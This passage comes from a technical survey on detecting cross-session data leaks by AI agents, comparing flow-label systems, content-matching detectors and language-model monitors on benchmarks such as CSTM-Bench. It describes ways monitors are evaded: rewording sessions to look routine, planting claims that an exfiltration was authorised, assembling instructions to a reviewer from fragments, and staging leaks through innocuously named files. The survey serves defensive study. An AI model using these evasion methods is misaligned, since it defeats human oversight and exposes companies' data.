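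SPA (2026) also plans first. It checks the whole plan against the labels before any tool runs, and rejects the plan if any tool call breaks a rule. If a message to the user breaks a rule, SPA blanks out the forbidden part and shows the rest. Another 2026 system, RANDORI, enforces its flow rules throughout a run. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) compares RANDORI with CaMeL and reports similar results for TypeGuard, which enforces comparable rules.

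Most of the published tests use AgentDojo, whose 97 tasks cover office work, chat, travel and banking. *Where Agent Defenses Fail* (2026) cites the result from CaMeL's own paper, and *Agent-Sentry* (2026) tests CaMeL against a rival system.

| System and test | Tasks completed without flow rules | With them |
|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, AgentDojo (cited in *Where Agent Defenses Fail*) | 84% (undefended agent) | 77% |
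| CaMeL, banking tasks (*The LLMbda Calculus*) | About twice as many | 37.5% |
| CaMeL, AgentDojo and a second benchmark (*Agent-Sentry*) | Not given | 31% |
| TypeGuard, chat tasks (*The LLMbda Calculus*) | 71% | 38% |
| SPA, single requests (Girrens and Wang) | 53% | 29% |
| SPA, tasks split into several requests (Girrens and Wang) | 62.5% | 35.3% |

The results for CaMeL differ partly because the tests used different tasks, models and policies. Both low figures also come from teams comparing CaMeL with their own systems. On the banking tasks, RANDORI's figure was roughly double CaMeL's 37.5%. In the *Agent-Sentry* test, CaMeL blocked 99.3% of attacks but took 26.6 seconds per run, about six times as long as the system it was compared with.

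Planning first had already reduced successful attacks on single requests to 4 in 949, and SPA's flow rules stopped the remaining four. But about 53% of runs stopped at the label check, mostly because the trust rule forbids using outside data in an important action, such as paying the amount stated on an invoice.

A company that only wants to trace secrets could leave out the trust rule, and the agent would probably fail fewer tasks. Girrens and Wang did not test the secrecy rule alone, so the size of this improvement is unknown. An auditor could also use the rules to raise alarms instead of blocking the agent. The agent would then finish its work, but about half of all runs would need a review under SPA's full rules.

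### Recognising the content itself

Labels work only if software tracks every step. If an employee retypes a summary into a new document, the label is lost, and the detector can only compare the outgoing text with sensitive sources.

Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, combine several kinds of comparison in NeuroTaint, a program that examines an agent's log after the work is done:

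- It adds a unique random marker to each document that the agent reads, and looks for the marker in what the agent sends.
- It finds the longest sequence that the source and the outgoing text share, and divides its length by that of the shorter text. A ratio of 0.15 is enough for a match.
- It converts both texts into lists of numbers, called embeddings, that are close together when the texts mean similar things. It flags a similarity of 0.60 or more, or 0.85 for text retrieved from memory.
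- It splits long sources into passages and compares each one separately, because one leaked sentence has little effect on the embedding of a long report.

If none of these finds a match, a language model judges whether the agent would have taken the same action without the source. This can show that a document influenced the agent even when the agent sent out none of the document's text.

Cai and colleagues tested NeuroTaint on 400 scenarios that they wrote for 20 agent frameworks. In 200 of them, data from a source reached or influenced a later action. NeuroTaint found 187 of these flows and wrongly flagged 16 of the 200 harmless scenarios. It found all 75 flows that a marker, shared text or a single passage could reveal, 75 of the 85 that required comparing meanings, and 37 of the 40 in which the source only influenced a decision. Repeated rewording caused most of the misses.

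The claim that the marker survives most summaries seems doubtful, since a good summary doesn't need to include a random string. NeuroTaint found the marker in all 15 scenarios designed for it, but those scenarios centered on exact copying.

#### Fragments

These comparisons don't join pieces of a secret that leave in separate messages. Waldrep's *One request looks clean. Five requests leak your AWS key* describes how the security tool Pipelock joins them. Pipelock keeps the data from an agent's recent requests in a buffer and searches the combined text for known key formats each time the agent sends something, so the request that completes a key triggers the alarm. It also measures the randomness of outgoing data and limits the total, because keys and encoded data look more random than ordinary text.

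Waldrep, who made the tool, cites no independent test of it. He acknowledges that the combined search misses encoded pieces and that the buffer covers only a few minutes by default. With that default, the tool would not connect sessions that are days apart. A longer window needs more memory, and Waldrep says joining data across sessions also raises privacy problems.

#### Decoy records

A decoy record is a false entry that a company plants in its data, such as an invented customer in a customer table. If the invented name appears in an outgoing message, some of the table has probably leaked. A company can also plant a false password and raise an alarm whenever someone tries to use it, which can reveal a leak even if nobody saw the password leave.

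Decoys are useful against slow leaks because the detector doesn't have to connect any sessions. Suppose 1% of the records in a customer table are decoys. A leak of 50 randomly chosen records contains at least one decoy about 39% of the time (1 − 0.99⁵⁰), and a leak of 300 records about 95% of the time. Dividing the leak among sessions doesn't change these figures. Decoys don't help detect a leak limited to particular real customers, though, and an agent may send a decoy during legitimate work.

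The table compares what each method can still recognise after the data changes.

| Method | Summarised | Re-encoded | Split into pieces |
|---|---|---|---|
| Exact pattern | Only if the value remains intact | Only if the detector decodes it | No |
| Whole-file fingerprint | No | No | No |
| Shared text | Only copied phrases | No | Only longer pieces |
| Fragment joining | No | No | Yes, within the time window |
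| Similar meaning | Often | No | Rarely for short pieces |
| Marker or decoy | Rarely | No | Only if it remains intact |
| Label | Yes | Yes | Yes |

Labels do best here, but only if software has tracked every step.

### When every document becomes secret

The main objection to labels is that anything a model has read may influence anything it writes afterwards. A cautious system must therefore copy the labels from everything the model has read to everything it writes. Eventually all data is labelled secret, and the labels no longer distinguish anything. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) calls this "label explosion".

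A "secret" label can spread quickly. Suppose 2% of a company's documents are secret and an agent reads 20 documents per session. About a third of sessions (1 − 0.98²⁰) then include a secret document, and everything the agent writes in those sessions is labeled secret. If each later session also reads three notes from the previous round, the label reaches about 80% of sessions in the second round and over 99% in the third.

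The spread of data labels was already a problem before language models. *An Empirical Study of Information Flows in Real-World JavaScript* (2019) found that in most of the programs tested, labels kept spreading as the program ran. Tracking only the direct movement of data, not its influence on decisions, reduced the spread by 45%.

Cai and colleagues' test on agents shows that treating a path from a source to a later action as strong evidence that data moved can cause many false alarms. They compared NeuroTaint with FIDES, which applies this rule in their setup. FIDES flagged 106 of the 200 harmless scenarios and found 108 of the 200 real flows. The comparison may be unfair to FIDES, which is designed to control agents as they run. It flagged nothing in four of the 20 frameworks, which suggests that the setup didn't suit them.

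#### Finer labels

One remedy is to label individual values instead of everything the model has read. If a customer's name is labeled internal and the card number secret, a message that contains only the name can keep the internal label. According to *PACE* (2026), the PACT system tracks the origin of each argument in a tool call. Hiding data in variables, as FIDES does, has a similar effect. However, such methods can slow agents considerably, according to *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026).

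Another approach is to pass on only the labels of inputs that influenced the output. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests labels that estimate how much information an output contains about each source. This would help most when an agent reads a hundred documents and uses two. However, a wrong estimate can remove a label from data that needs it, which can cause a leak to be missed. MemLineage's simulation shows how such errors can build up over several summaries.

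NeuroTaint avoids many false alarms by comparing content, but it wrongly flagged all 14 harmless scenarios in which the output only concerned the same topic as the source. This matters for a company whose agents write about the same few customers every day. If one run in a thousand were a leak and NeuroTaint performed as it did in the test, about one alarm in 86 would be real. When Cai and colleagues had Claude Opus 4.6 review the alarms, it removed all 16 false ones, but also eight of the 187 real flows.

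#### Isolated sub-agents

A company can have a sub-agent read a secret document and return only a short answer. If the main agent needs to know whether a project is within budget, the sub-agent can read the salary file and answer yes or no. The main agent never sees the salaries, so its other work doesn't inherit the salary file's label.

The answer still depends on the file, so SPA keeps the file's label on the answer, even though the model that reads the file has no tools. Someone may decide that a single yes or no is safe to release, but many such answers can together reveal more, so each should count towards a disclosure budget.

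#### Release decisions

Some tasks can't be completed unless someone can lift a restriction. *The LLMbda Calculus* describes three banking tasks in which the agent must read an untrusted file and act on it. When the rules are enforced, the agent can't finish these tasks until someone vouches for the data. RTBAS, another system that *PACE* describes, asks the user when its automatic check can't establish that an action is safe.

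*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) describes FlowSeal, a system that automates part of the decision. It keeps a list of every record the agent has opened. Whenever the agent tries to write or share something, a separate checker compares the outgoing text with those records and returns only "safe" or "blocked". The checker can recognise a paraphrase or a coded reference because it has the original records. Ordinary program code starts the check, so an attacker can't avoid it by persuading the agent to skip it.

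Human approval is particularly weak against distributed leaks because each request can look as ordinary to the approver as it did to the agent. An approver who sees only "send metrics.txt to a monitoring service" would probably agree. The request should also show the path the data took from the database file and how much the same user has already sent. Each approval should apply to one item and one recipient, because removing a label from a shared summary would also remove it from everything that later sessions derive from that summary.

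### Tests across sessions

Cai and colleagues' benchmark includes 30 flows that cross from one session or agent to another. NeuroTaint found 28 of them and FIDES found five. In one scenario, an agent stores a confidential forecast for "Project Atlas", and three days later it uses the figures in a report. FIDES has access only to the second session, where the agent retrieves a note and writes the report. NeuroTaint saves its graph and labels at the end of each session and reloads them for the next, so it can connect the report to the forecast.

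This is direct evidence that stored labels help, but all 30 cases were real flows, so the result doesn't show how often NeuroTaint would raise false alarms across sessions. The same team designed both the detector and the scenarios. Of the frameworks tested, NeuroTaint did worst on Mem0, a memory system for agents, where it found seven of ten flows. It also needs logs of the model's intermediate reasoning and memory operations, which many companies don't keep.

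SPA's test with several requests has limited relevance to leaks across sessions, because each task's two to five requests belonged to one session. When the data from an earlier request was available, SPA retrieved it about 90% of the time with the flow rules on. Girrens and Wang acknowledge that their attacks were a weak test of harm delayed through memory.

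## How well do language-model monitors recognise a leak spread over sessions?

Counting, labelling and text comparison can't show whether six requests that each look plausible make sense together as ordinary work. A person who reads the whole log might be able to tell, but security teams rarely have the time. *Large Language Models for Security Operations Centers* (Habibzadeh, Fevzi and Ebrahimi Atani, 2025) describes teams that fall behind on alerts and can't fill vacancies. This is why many companies want language models to read logs for them.

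### Three readers, two sets of scenarios

Azarafrooz's CSTM-Bench, the source of the six-session plan, tests how well language-model monitors recognise leaks spread over sessions. It has two sets of 54 scenarios. In each set, 26 scenarios contain an attack and 28 contain only harmless work. Some attacks are leaks, while others aim to gain extra permissions or plant instructions in an agent's memory. Each scenario comes with a short policy for the agent, and the monitor must decide whether someone is leading the agent to break it.

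Half of the harmless scenarios show ordinary work. Azarafrooz designed the other 14 to be confusing. In some of these, a long run of routine approvals ends with a request to approve one more item. In others, two agents each receive half of a harmless instruction.

Claude Sonnet 4.6 judged the scenarios in three ways:

- As a per-session judge, it read one session at a time. A scenario counted as flagged if the judge flagged any of its sessions.
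- As a whole-log reader, it received all the messages in order and gave one verdict.
- As a buffer reader, it received up to 50 messages that a separate program had selected as the most unusual for that agent.

All three read what users wrote to the agent, not the agent's tool calls.

The first set contains the attacks as the generator wrote them. For the second, a stronger model, Claude Opus 4.7, reworded the sessions the judge had flagged to make them look harmless, but kept the file paths, addresses and tool names that connected them. It succeeded with 90 of 113 sessions, and the other 23 stayed unchanged.

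| Reader | Attacks found, original | Attacks found, reworded | False alarms, ordinary work | False alarms, confusing cases |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Per-session judge | 26 of 26 | 14 of 26 | 3 of 14 | 9 of 14 |
| Whole log | 23 of 26 | 13 of 26 | 0 of 14 | 7 of 14 |
| Buffer | 25 of 26 | 19 of 26 | 0 of 14 | 3 of 14 |

The judge flagged all the original attacks, but it also flagged 12 of the 28 harmless scenarios. After the rewording, it flagged 54% of the attacks and 43% of the harmless scenarios, so its alarms barely distinguished the two. The buffer reader did much better, flagging 73% of the attacks and 11% of the harmless scenarios. Even so, if one task in a thousand were an attack, only about one in 150 of its alarms would be real.

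### Attacks that no single session reveals

After the rewording, the judge missed 12 of the 26 attacks entirely. (The paper's text gives this number as 14, but that is how many the judge still flagged.) A monitor has to combine sessions to find these 12, so they are the benchmark's best examples of distributed attacks.

The whole-log reader found five of them. According to Azarafrooz, the structure of these five spreads them across sessions, regardless of how they are worded. In one, someone gathers credentials in stages, and in another, a user switches identity between sessions. So the same tools, files or user identifiers keep reappearing in the log.

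The buffer reader found six of the 12 attacks in which every session looked harmless by itself, only one more than the whole-log reader. Most of its overall lead comes from the other 14 attacks, in which at least one session looked suspicious by itself. It found 13 of those, and the whole-log reader found eight. The results suggest that a buffer helps keep harmless messages from hiding a suspicious one, but they are much weaker evidence that it helps when every session looks harmless.

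The next table shows the results for the four attack types closest to a data leak, after rewording.

| Attack type | Per-session judge | Whole log | Buffer |
|---|---|---|---|
| Staged exfiltration, as in the six-session plan | Found | Found | Found |
| Disguise by rewriting | Found | Missed | Found |
| Mosaic attack | Found | Missed | Found |
| Gathering credentials in stages | Missed | Found | Found |

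These results are encouraging for the buffer, but each row is a single scenario. The judge's success with the mosaic attack is odd, since the individual questions should look harmless. Either one of the questions revealed the attack or the judge was right by luck, which is possible because it also flagged many harmless scenarios.

Five of the 26 attacks escaped all three readers. In one, the attacker disguised a request by having sub-agents pass it on, and in another, several agents coordinated without an explicit plan. A company that ran all three readers would have found the other 21 attacks, but would also have received false alarms on at least 12 of the 28 harmless scenarios.

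### How the buffer selects messages

Before the test, a language model turns the agent's policy into example sentences that comply with it or violate it. A program converts these into embeddings and calculates the centre μ and the spread Σ of the compliant ones. It then scores each new message, whose embedding is x:

s(x) = ½ (x − μ)ᵀ Σ⁻¹ (x − μ)

w(x) = max(0, s(x) − τ)

The score s grows with the square of the message's distance from the centre, measured relative to the usual spread. The threshold τ is set so that nine in ten compliant examples score below it. If embeddings had one dimension and followed a bell curve, τ would be about 1.35. A message one standard deviation from the centre would score 0.5 and stay out of the buffer. A message three standard deviations away would score 4.5 and enter with a weight w of about 3.15.

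When the buffer is full, the program merges two similar entries, favouring pairs with more weight, and keeps the text of the heavier entry. The monitor receives the entries heaviest first.

In the attack scenarios, however, the buffer never filled up, because it had room for 50 messages and Azarafrooz reports between 22 and 40 in each original attack log. The test therefore doesn't show what happens when the program has to condense a long history. The buffer reader's advantage must come from leaving out messages below the threshold, from the order of the remaining messages, or from the different instructions that the model received with the buffer. Azarafrooz acknowledges not knowing how much the instructions contributed.

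#### A buffer that does fill up

*Benchmarking Mitigations Against Covert Misuse* (Brown, Sabbaghi and colleagues, 2025) tested a buffer on longer histories, in which simulated users had sent a model between 10 and 400 queries. A classifier scored every query, the buffer kept the 30 most suspicious ones per user, and a model read them and judged the user. The harmful users requested dangerous knowledge about biology or cybersecurity in harmless-looking parts. No company data was involved, but the pattern resembles a mosaic attack because the user combines the answers outside the system.

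Brown and colleagues report their results as AUC, the area under the curve that plots recall against the false-positive rate at every possible alarm threshold. It equals the chance that a detector scores a randomly chosen harmful case higher than a randomly chosen harmless one, so guessing gives 0.5 and perfect separation gives 1. Suppose two harmful users score 9 and 5, and three harmless users score 7, 3 and 2. The harmful user scores higher in five of the six possible pairs of a harmful and a harmless user, so the AUC is 5/6, or about 0.83.

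| Detector | AUC, single queries | AUC, with the buffer |
|---|---|---|
| Llama Guard 3 8B, a safety classifier | 0.60 | Not reported |
| The same classifier, trained on similar attacks | 0.76 | 0.79 |
| Llama 3 70B, a larger general model | 0.71 | 0.86 |

The larger model gained far more from the buffer, probably because it was better at working out what 30 separate queries had in common.

Brown and colleagues also tested a simpler monitor that read only a user's most recent queries (fewer than 100). It worked when about half of the queries were harmful, but when harmful queries were rare, harmless ones pushed them out of the window before enough had accumulated. The buffer avoids this by keeping suspicious queries however old they are.

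Even with the buffer, false alarms rose sharply when most of a harmful user's queries were harmless. This is probably because the 30 most suspicious of 400 harmless queries look worse than a typical harmless query, which makes busy harmless users harder to tell apart from harmful ones. The problem would be larger for an agent that serves a whole department. The method also only works if queries can be linked to the user who sent them.

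### Why more context did not help

Giving the model the whole log didn't fully solve the problem of scattered evidence in CSTM-Bench. The whole-log reader received every message but still missed three of the original attacks and half of the reworded ones. Every log fit easily in the model's context window, which holds a million tokens (pieces of words). The longest log filled 14.8% of the window, and the average log filled 5.1%.

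In six of the reworded scenarios, the judge flagged at least one session by itself, but the whole-log reader, which had the same session in its log, did not flag the scenario. Azarafrooz attributes this to dilution, meaning that when most sessions look like authorised work, the model's single verdict on the log tends towards "routine, with a few oddities". The two readers also had different instructions, and the judge raised alarms much more readily, so dilution may not be the whole explanation.

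The test diluted the attack messages only mildly. The original attack scenarios averaged about four attack messages out of 26, whereas a slow leak in a company's log might account for six in a hundred thousand.

Two other studies, both cited in *Towards a Unified Misuse Monitoring Benchmark* (Pramod, Oldfield and Bibi, 2026), support the idea that monitors need selected evidence more than additional text. Arike and colleagues found that monitors often do better when they see less. Hills and colleagues studied an agent that spread a hidden task over several proposed software changes. Showing monitors more of the history did not expose the agent, and only a monitor that tracked suspicious signs as they built up caught it.

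### How firm are the CSTM-Bench results?

Azarafrooz advises readers to treat every figure as a rough indication. With 26 attacks, the 95% confidence interval for recall on reworded attacks runs from about 54% to 86% for the buffer reader and from 32% to 68% for the whole-log reader. A paired comparison is more informative, because both read the same scenarios. Of the eight reworded attacks that only one reader found, the buffer reader found seven. If the two were equally good, a split at least this uneven would happen by chance about 7% of the time. The buffer reader is therefore probably better, but this is far from certain.

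The absence of false alarms in the 14 scenarios of ordinary work is also weak evidence that the false-alarm rate is low. A monitor that wrongly flagged 19% of such scenarios would still have about a 5% chance of flagging none of the 14 (0.81^14 ≈ 0.05).

CSTM-Bench's scenarios are synthetic and short. A language model wrote the sessions from templates, so the harmless work is probably tidier than it would be in a real company. The design allows mosaic attacks of up to 200 sessions, but the mosaic scenario in the test has 29 messages in total, including the harmless ones.

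All three readers and the model that did the rewording belong to the Claude family. Azarafrooz doesn't claim that the reworded sessions would mislead models from other companies. The rewording was aimed at the per-session judge, and the other readers did worse as a side effect. Nobody tested rewording aimed at the program that fills the buffer, and the buffer reader would probably do worse against it.

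Azarafrooz works for the security company Intrinsec AI and also tested an undisclosed commercial buffer, whose results the paper leaves out. The scenarios are public, but the code that generated them, selected the messages and scored the results is not. Another team could run its own monitor on them but would have to rebuild the selection program from the paper's description.

The paper's overall score is a poor guide to which reader is best:

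CSTM = 0.7 × F₁ + 0.3 × stability

F₁ combines recall with the share of harmless scenarios that the reader did not flag. Stability measures how much of the buffer stays in the same order from one message to the next, because a stable order makes the model cheaper to run. The whole-log reader has no buffer, so it automatically gets the maximum stability score, while the buffer reader gets 0.44. As a result, the whole-log reader scores higher on the reworded set, 0.72 against 0.69, although it found six fewer attacks and raised four more false alarms.

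### Do requests reveal more than logs?

Azarafrooz's reason for having the readers judge requests is the data processing inequality. In symbols, the attacker's goal G leads to the request R, then to what the agent executes, E, and finally to the log L:

G → R → E → L

I(G; R) ≥ I(G; E) ≥ I(G; L)

Here I(G; R) is the mutual information between the goal and the request, which measures how much a reader can learn about one from the other. It is zero if they are unrelated.

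The inequality holds only if the goal influences the log through the request alone. If an attacker plants instructions in an email that the agent reads, the goal enters through a tool result T:

G → T → E ← R

The user's request is now unrelated to the attacker's goal, so I(G; R) = 0, while the log of the agent's actions can reveal a lot about that goal. Counting tool results as requests could repair the chain, but then the monitor has to read tool results, which a company would normally get from its logs.

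This repair doesn't help with accidental leaks, such as the wrong notes attached to a meeting recap, because there is no attacker's goal G to trace.

The theorem also doesn't cover how well a model uses the information it receives. The buffer is computed from the requests in the whole log, so by the same inequality it can't contain more information about the attack than they do. Yet the model found more attacks when it read the buffer. A log that stores the requests next to the tool calls contains at least as much information as the requests alone, so a company doesn't have to choose between requests and tool calls.

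#### Judging requests or actions

Pramod and colleagues compared monitors that judge what a conversation is about with monitors that judge what the agent does. They tested 17 monitor configurations on their benchmark of about 6,200 synthetic transcripts. In some transcripts, a user splits a harmful task into small requests, and in others, hostile instructions reach the agent through a tool result.

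The next table shows the AUC of four monitors that used the model Gemma 4.

| What the monitor reads and judges | Split tasks | Injected instructions |
|---|---|---|
| The agent's current message, judged as an action | 0.90 | 0.92 |
| The conversation so far, judged by the intent of its tasks | 0.96 | 0.52 |
| The conversation so far, judged by the agent's current action | 0.95 | 0.99 |
| Quotes that another model call extracts from the conversation | 0.95 | 0.99 |

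For injected instructions, judging the intent of the tasks worked hardly better than guessing, largely because Pramod and colleagues put the same hostile instructions in both harmful and harmless transcripts. The agent follows them in the harmful transcripts and refuses in the harmless ones, so a monitor that reacts to the instructions will flag both.

A security team may well want to hear about a failed attack, but to find out whether data left, it needs a monitor that looks at the agent's actions. The table suggests that such a monitor performs almost as well when a task is split. CSTM-Bench's readers saw only requests, so they would probably do better with the tool calls as well, although nobody has tested this.

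All the transcripts are single conversations, so the monitors never had to connect sessions. Conversations in the original split tasks had a median of seven user requests. A monitor that saw one message at a time reached 0.90 on split tasks, which suggests that many of these tasks contained a step that looked suspicious by itself.

### Did the alarm come in time?

AUC also doesn't measure timing, which matters because a company can't recall leaked data. Pramod and colleagues therefore marked a window in each harmful transcript, from when the agent first commits to something harmful until it carries out the overall goal. In one transcript, the agent commits to sending a phishing email at message 25 and mails the stolen passwords to the attacker at message 68. An alarm at message 1 would interrupt the agent before it had done anything wrong, and one at message 71 would be too late.

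The table shows how often each monitor found the harm at all and how often its first alarm fell inside the window, with each monitor raising false alarms on at most 10% of harmless transcripts.

| Monitor judges | Split tasks found | Found in the window | Injections found | Found in the window |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Current message | 78% | 33% | 82% | 62% |
| Intent of the tasks | 96% | 17% | – | – |
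| Current action, with the conversation | 94% | 43% | 99.7% | 95% |
| Extracted quotes | 93% | 50% | 99.5% | 90% |

The monitor that judged intent has no result for injections because it couldn't keep false alarms below 63%.

On split tasks, nearly all the badly timed alarms came too early. Pramod and colleagues inspected 21 of them and found that many concerned preparatory steps, while one came before any harmful content. The low scores are partly due to a strict definition of good timing, since allowing alarms up to four messages before the window raised the scores by 14 to 27 percentage points. For a company that mainly wants to keep its data, an early alarm is much better than a late one. But an analyst who investigates an early alarm may find little evidence and close the case before the leak happens.

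The timing scores are somewhat inflated because Pramod and colleagues chose the alarm thresholds using the same transcripts they scored. With thresholds chosen on separate data, the scores on split tasks fell by about 12 points on average.

The monitors also raised false alarms when the agent refused a request. In one test, the agent declined just as it would have begun to do harm, but monitors that judged actions still flagged 28% to 48% of these transcripts with most of the models tested.

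Like CSTM-Bench, this benchmark is synthetic. One model wrote all the agent's messages and simulated all the tool results. Language models also marked where the harm began in the split tasks. When two models marked the same 40 transcripts, they chose the same message in 67.5% of them. The benchmark doesn't test attackers who try to avoid the monitor.

CSTM-Bench provides even less evidence on timing. Its main measure is meant to count attacks found before the decisive step, but the whole-log and buffer readers each gave one verdict after all the messages had arrived. If the verdict was positive, Azarafrooz counted every part of the attack as detected. The buffer reader therefore recognised its 19 attacks only afterwards, too late to stop them.

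### Finding exfiltration in system logs

For coding agents, the most complete record often comes from the operating system's logs. *Benchmarking and Exploring the Capabilities of LLMs for Attack Investigations* (Anand, Kantchelian and colleagues, 2026) tested how well language models find attacks in such logs. Its benchmark, AuditBench, contains 51 scenarios from Linux and Windows machines, and seven of these scenarios include data exfiltration. To score a hit, a model had to name the exfiltrated file and the time of the transfer. The logs record programs, files and network connections, but no conversations with an agent.

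The researchers condensed the logs into lines. Each line describes one action between a program and a file or address, much like an edge in a provenance graph. They then gave the lines to five models from 2025 in blocks of 400.

| Model | Transfers found | False alarms |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 7 of 7 | 3 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 7 of 7 | 18 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 7 of 7 | 37 |
| GPT-5 mini | 5 of 7 | 4 |
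| Llama 4 Maverick | 3 of 7 | 5 |

The models did best on the exfiltration task. GPT-5 raised three false alarms in roughly 76,000 log lines, which cover less than two hours of activity. At that rate, one machine would produce nearly 40 false alarms a day. This estimate is crude because it is based on three errors and deliberately busy logs, but it shows why a false-positive rate per log line can be misleading. A company would probably use such a model to investigate an alert, which is what Anand and colleagues designed the test for.

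Increasing the block length from 400 to 1,600 lines of log did not help in the researchers' own recordings either. Both Gemini models found all five transfers with 400 lines, but with 1,600 lines Gemini 2.5 Flash found three and Gemini 2.5 Pro found two. With 200 lines, both found only two, perhaps because some blocks then contained the transfer without the steps that explained it. Five scenarios are too few to identify a best length.

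More precise instructions made a clearer difference. The researchers described how attackers typically move data and told the models to ignore temporary files and similar system data. GPT-5 mini's F₁ score on exfiltration, which combines recall with the share of alarms that are real, rose from 0.12 to 0.62. The other three models in this comparison also improved, mainly because they raised fewer false alarms. A company could add its own facts to the instructions, such as the address of its backup service.

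The models also made different mistakes. Across all tasks, 350 distinct false alarms each came from only one or two of the five models, and 19 came from four or more. Requiring several models to agree should therefore remove many false alarms, but it would also miss transfers that only one model recognises.

The longest exfiltration scenario lasts 36 minutes, so these tests don't show whether a model would connect a file read in March with a transfer in April. A company would first need another method, such as a fingerprint match or a provenance graph, to link the two records, and a model could then explain what they mean. When the models correctly identified exfiltration, their explanations were mostly accurate, scoring an average of 4.2 out of 5 when another language model compared them with the known facts. None of the attacks was designed to mislead the models.

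### When the log misleads its reader

An attacker may have written the requests, file names and tool results that a monitor reads. That text can influence the monitor in the same way a hostile web page influences an agent.

Azarafrooz includes two types of attack in CSTM-Bench that use text in the log to influence the monitor. Some attacks end with an extra session containing a claim that everything before it was an authorised exercise and a request that the reviewer withdraw the alarm. The benchmark counts a withdrawal as a missed attack, because the monitor cannot verify the claim from the text. In other attacks, messages that look harmless one at a time form an instruction to the monitor when a program joins them into a single log. This instruction reaches a monitor that reads the whole log but not one that judges each session separately.

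Azarafrooz's claim that the buffer reader avoids this second problem seems too optimistic. The buffer passes on the original text of the messages it selects, and it would probably select a message addressed to a reviewer, because such a message is unusual for a support or deployment agent. The paper gives no separate results for these attacks.

Text can mislead a monitor without giving it instructions. The reworded sessions mostly presented the work as approved or routine, which halved the whole-log reader's recall compared with the original set. Names can also mislead monitors. Anand and colleagues found that 18 of the 19 false alarms shared by at least four models relied heavily on the names of files, programs or tasks. In one case, several models treated a scheduled task as an attack largely because its name suggested that it cleared logs. A monitor that relies so heavily on names may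 also overlook a file with an ordinary name, such as the "metrics.txt" that carries the encoded summary in the six-session plan.

The safest response is to check claims against records that the author of the text can't change. If a session contains a claim that a transfer was approved, the monitor should look for the grant in the authorisation server's log. A fingerprint match between a protected file and an outgoing attachment also remains valid regardless of the surrounding messages. A company can therefore let a language model explain, rank and add alarms, but it should not let the model cancel an alarm based on such a record. People will then have to review some false alarms that the model could have removed.

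## How is activity under different accounts and agents connected?

A running total and a monitor that reads a user's history both work only if the detector can identify which records belong together. Most systems group records by account, because nearly every log contains an account name. But a person can have several accounts or share one with other people.

### Choosing what to count

Suppose a company lets each account send 50 customer records a month to outside addresses. An employee runs five agents, each with its own account, and each agent sends 40 records. The employee has sent 200 records without any account reaching its limit.

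Shared accounts cause the opposite problem, because one person's leak is hidden in everyone's combined traffic. Suppose 30 people use a help-desk agent through one service account, an account that belongs to a program instead of a person. Each person's requests send an average of 20 records a day with a standard deviation of 5, as in the CUSUM example, until one person starts leaking 5 more a day. CUSUM would find the leak in about ten days if it tracked that person's total separately. But the whole account sends 600 records a day with a standard deviation of about 27, so the leak is less than a fifth of a standard deviation. The same test, scaled to the larger total, would typically need more than four months.

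Delegation can also hide how much data was sent in total. If a main agent reads 200 records and has four sub-agents email 50 each, a count per agent shows one agent that sent nothing and four that stayed within the limit, while a count per user shows that all 200 were sent.

A company can keep more than one total of the records sent, but this produces more false alarms. A total for each outside destination is especially useful because it doesn't require anyone to link the senders. If five accounts that look unrelated all send records to the same address, the total for that address includes all their transfers.

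### Ways to link accounts

Inside a company, the best link is a verified identity. When an employee signs in, the agent receives a delegation token, a signed statement of whom it acts for. The agent passes this token to its sub-agents. If the logs keep the token's identity fields, investigators can trace every action to a person.

Identity checks are less reliable when the users are outside customers. The Paypers' *Real-time link analysis*, an interview with Anita Ilango of the identity-checking company Persona, describes "identity mules", people whom fraudsters pay to open an account, pass the selfie check and hand over the login. The account is then verified under a real person's name but used by someone else.

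Investigators can connect accounts by looking for what they have in common, a technique called link analysis. According to Ilango, fraudsters often reuse a device or document template and change only one element, such as the name or portrait. A shared payment card or network address can also connect accounts.

Behaviour can also link accounts. If two accounts start and stop within seconds of each other for weeks, they probably run on the same schedule. Hundreds of accounts that send slight variations of one long request may share an operator, although people also copy popular prompts from public websites.

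### Five accounts, two groups

The table shows five invented accounts on a platform that hosts agents for 10,000 customers.

| Account | Payment card | Device | Outside destination | Network |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A | Card 1 | Laptop 1 | store-1.example | Office |
| B | Card 1 | Laptop 2 | store-2.example | Home 1 |
| C | Card 2 | Laptop 2 | store-3.example | Home 2 |
| D | Card 3 | Laptop 3 | store-4.example | Office |
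| E | Card 4 | Laptop 4 | store-4.example | Home 3 |

If we ignore the network at first, accounts A, B and C form a group because A and B share a card and B and C share a laptop, even though A and C have nothing in common. D and E form a second group because they send data to the same destination. If each account sends 40 records, the groups send 120 and 80, and both exceed a limit of 50.

The network column makes this result unreliable, because A and D connect from the same office and that one link merges all five accounts. If 300 of the platform's customers work in that building, A and D are probably unrelated.

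One remedy is to give each link a weight that depends on how rare the shared value is:

w = log₂(N / n)

A link's score is log₂(N / n), where N is the number of accounts on the platform and n is the number that have the shared value. On a platform with 10,000 accounts, a card that only two accounts use scores log₂(10,000 / 2), or about 12.3. The shared laptop and destination score the same if no other account uses them. The office network, which 300 accounts use, scores log₂(10,000 / 300), or about 5.1. This is below a threshold of 8, so the network doesn't link the two groups and they stay separate.

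Adding up the scores of weak links can cause the same error again. Suppose A and D are also both active from nine to five, like 1,000 other accounts. That link scores 3.3, which brings the total to 8.4, above the threshold. But adding the scores is valid only if the two attributes are independent, in which case only about 30 accounts would have both. Nearly all 300 people in the office may keep those hours.

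A wrong link does more damage when it joins larger groups. If it joins two groups of 20 accounts, it creates 400 false pairs, and the groups' combined activity may trigger an investigation of people who did nothing unusual. The software should store the reason for every link so that an analyst can remove a wrong link and recompute the groups.

### Model extraction through thousands of accounts

The largest published examples of account linking concern distillation, which means training a weaker AI model on the outputs of a stronger one. Anthropic's *Detecting and preventing distillation attacks* (February 2026) accuses three Chinese AI companies of using about 24,000 fraudulent accounts to hold more than 16 million exchanges with its model Claude. No agent leaked data in this case, because the customers requested and kept Claude's answers themselves, in breach of the terms of service. The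 case is still relevant because Anthropic also had to find out which accounts belonged together.

| Company | Exchanges | Evidence that Anthropic describes |
|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek | Over 150,000 | Shared payment methods, identical patterns and synchronised timing; request metadata that led to specific researchers |
| Moonshot AI | Over 3.4 million | Request metadata that matched the public profiles of senior staff |
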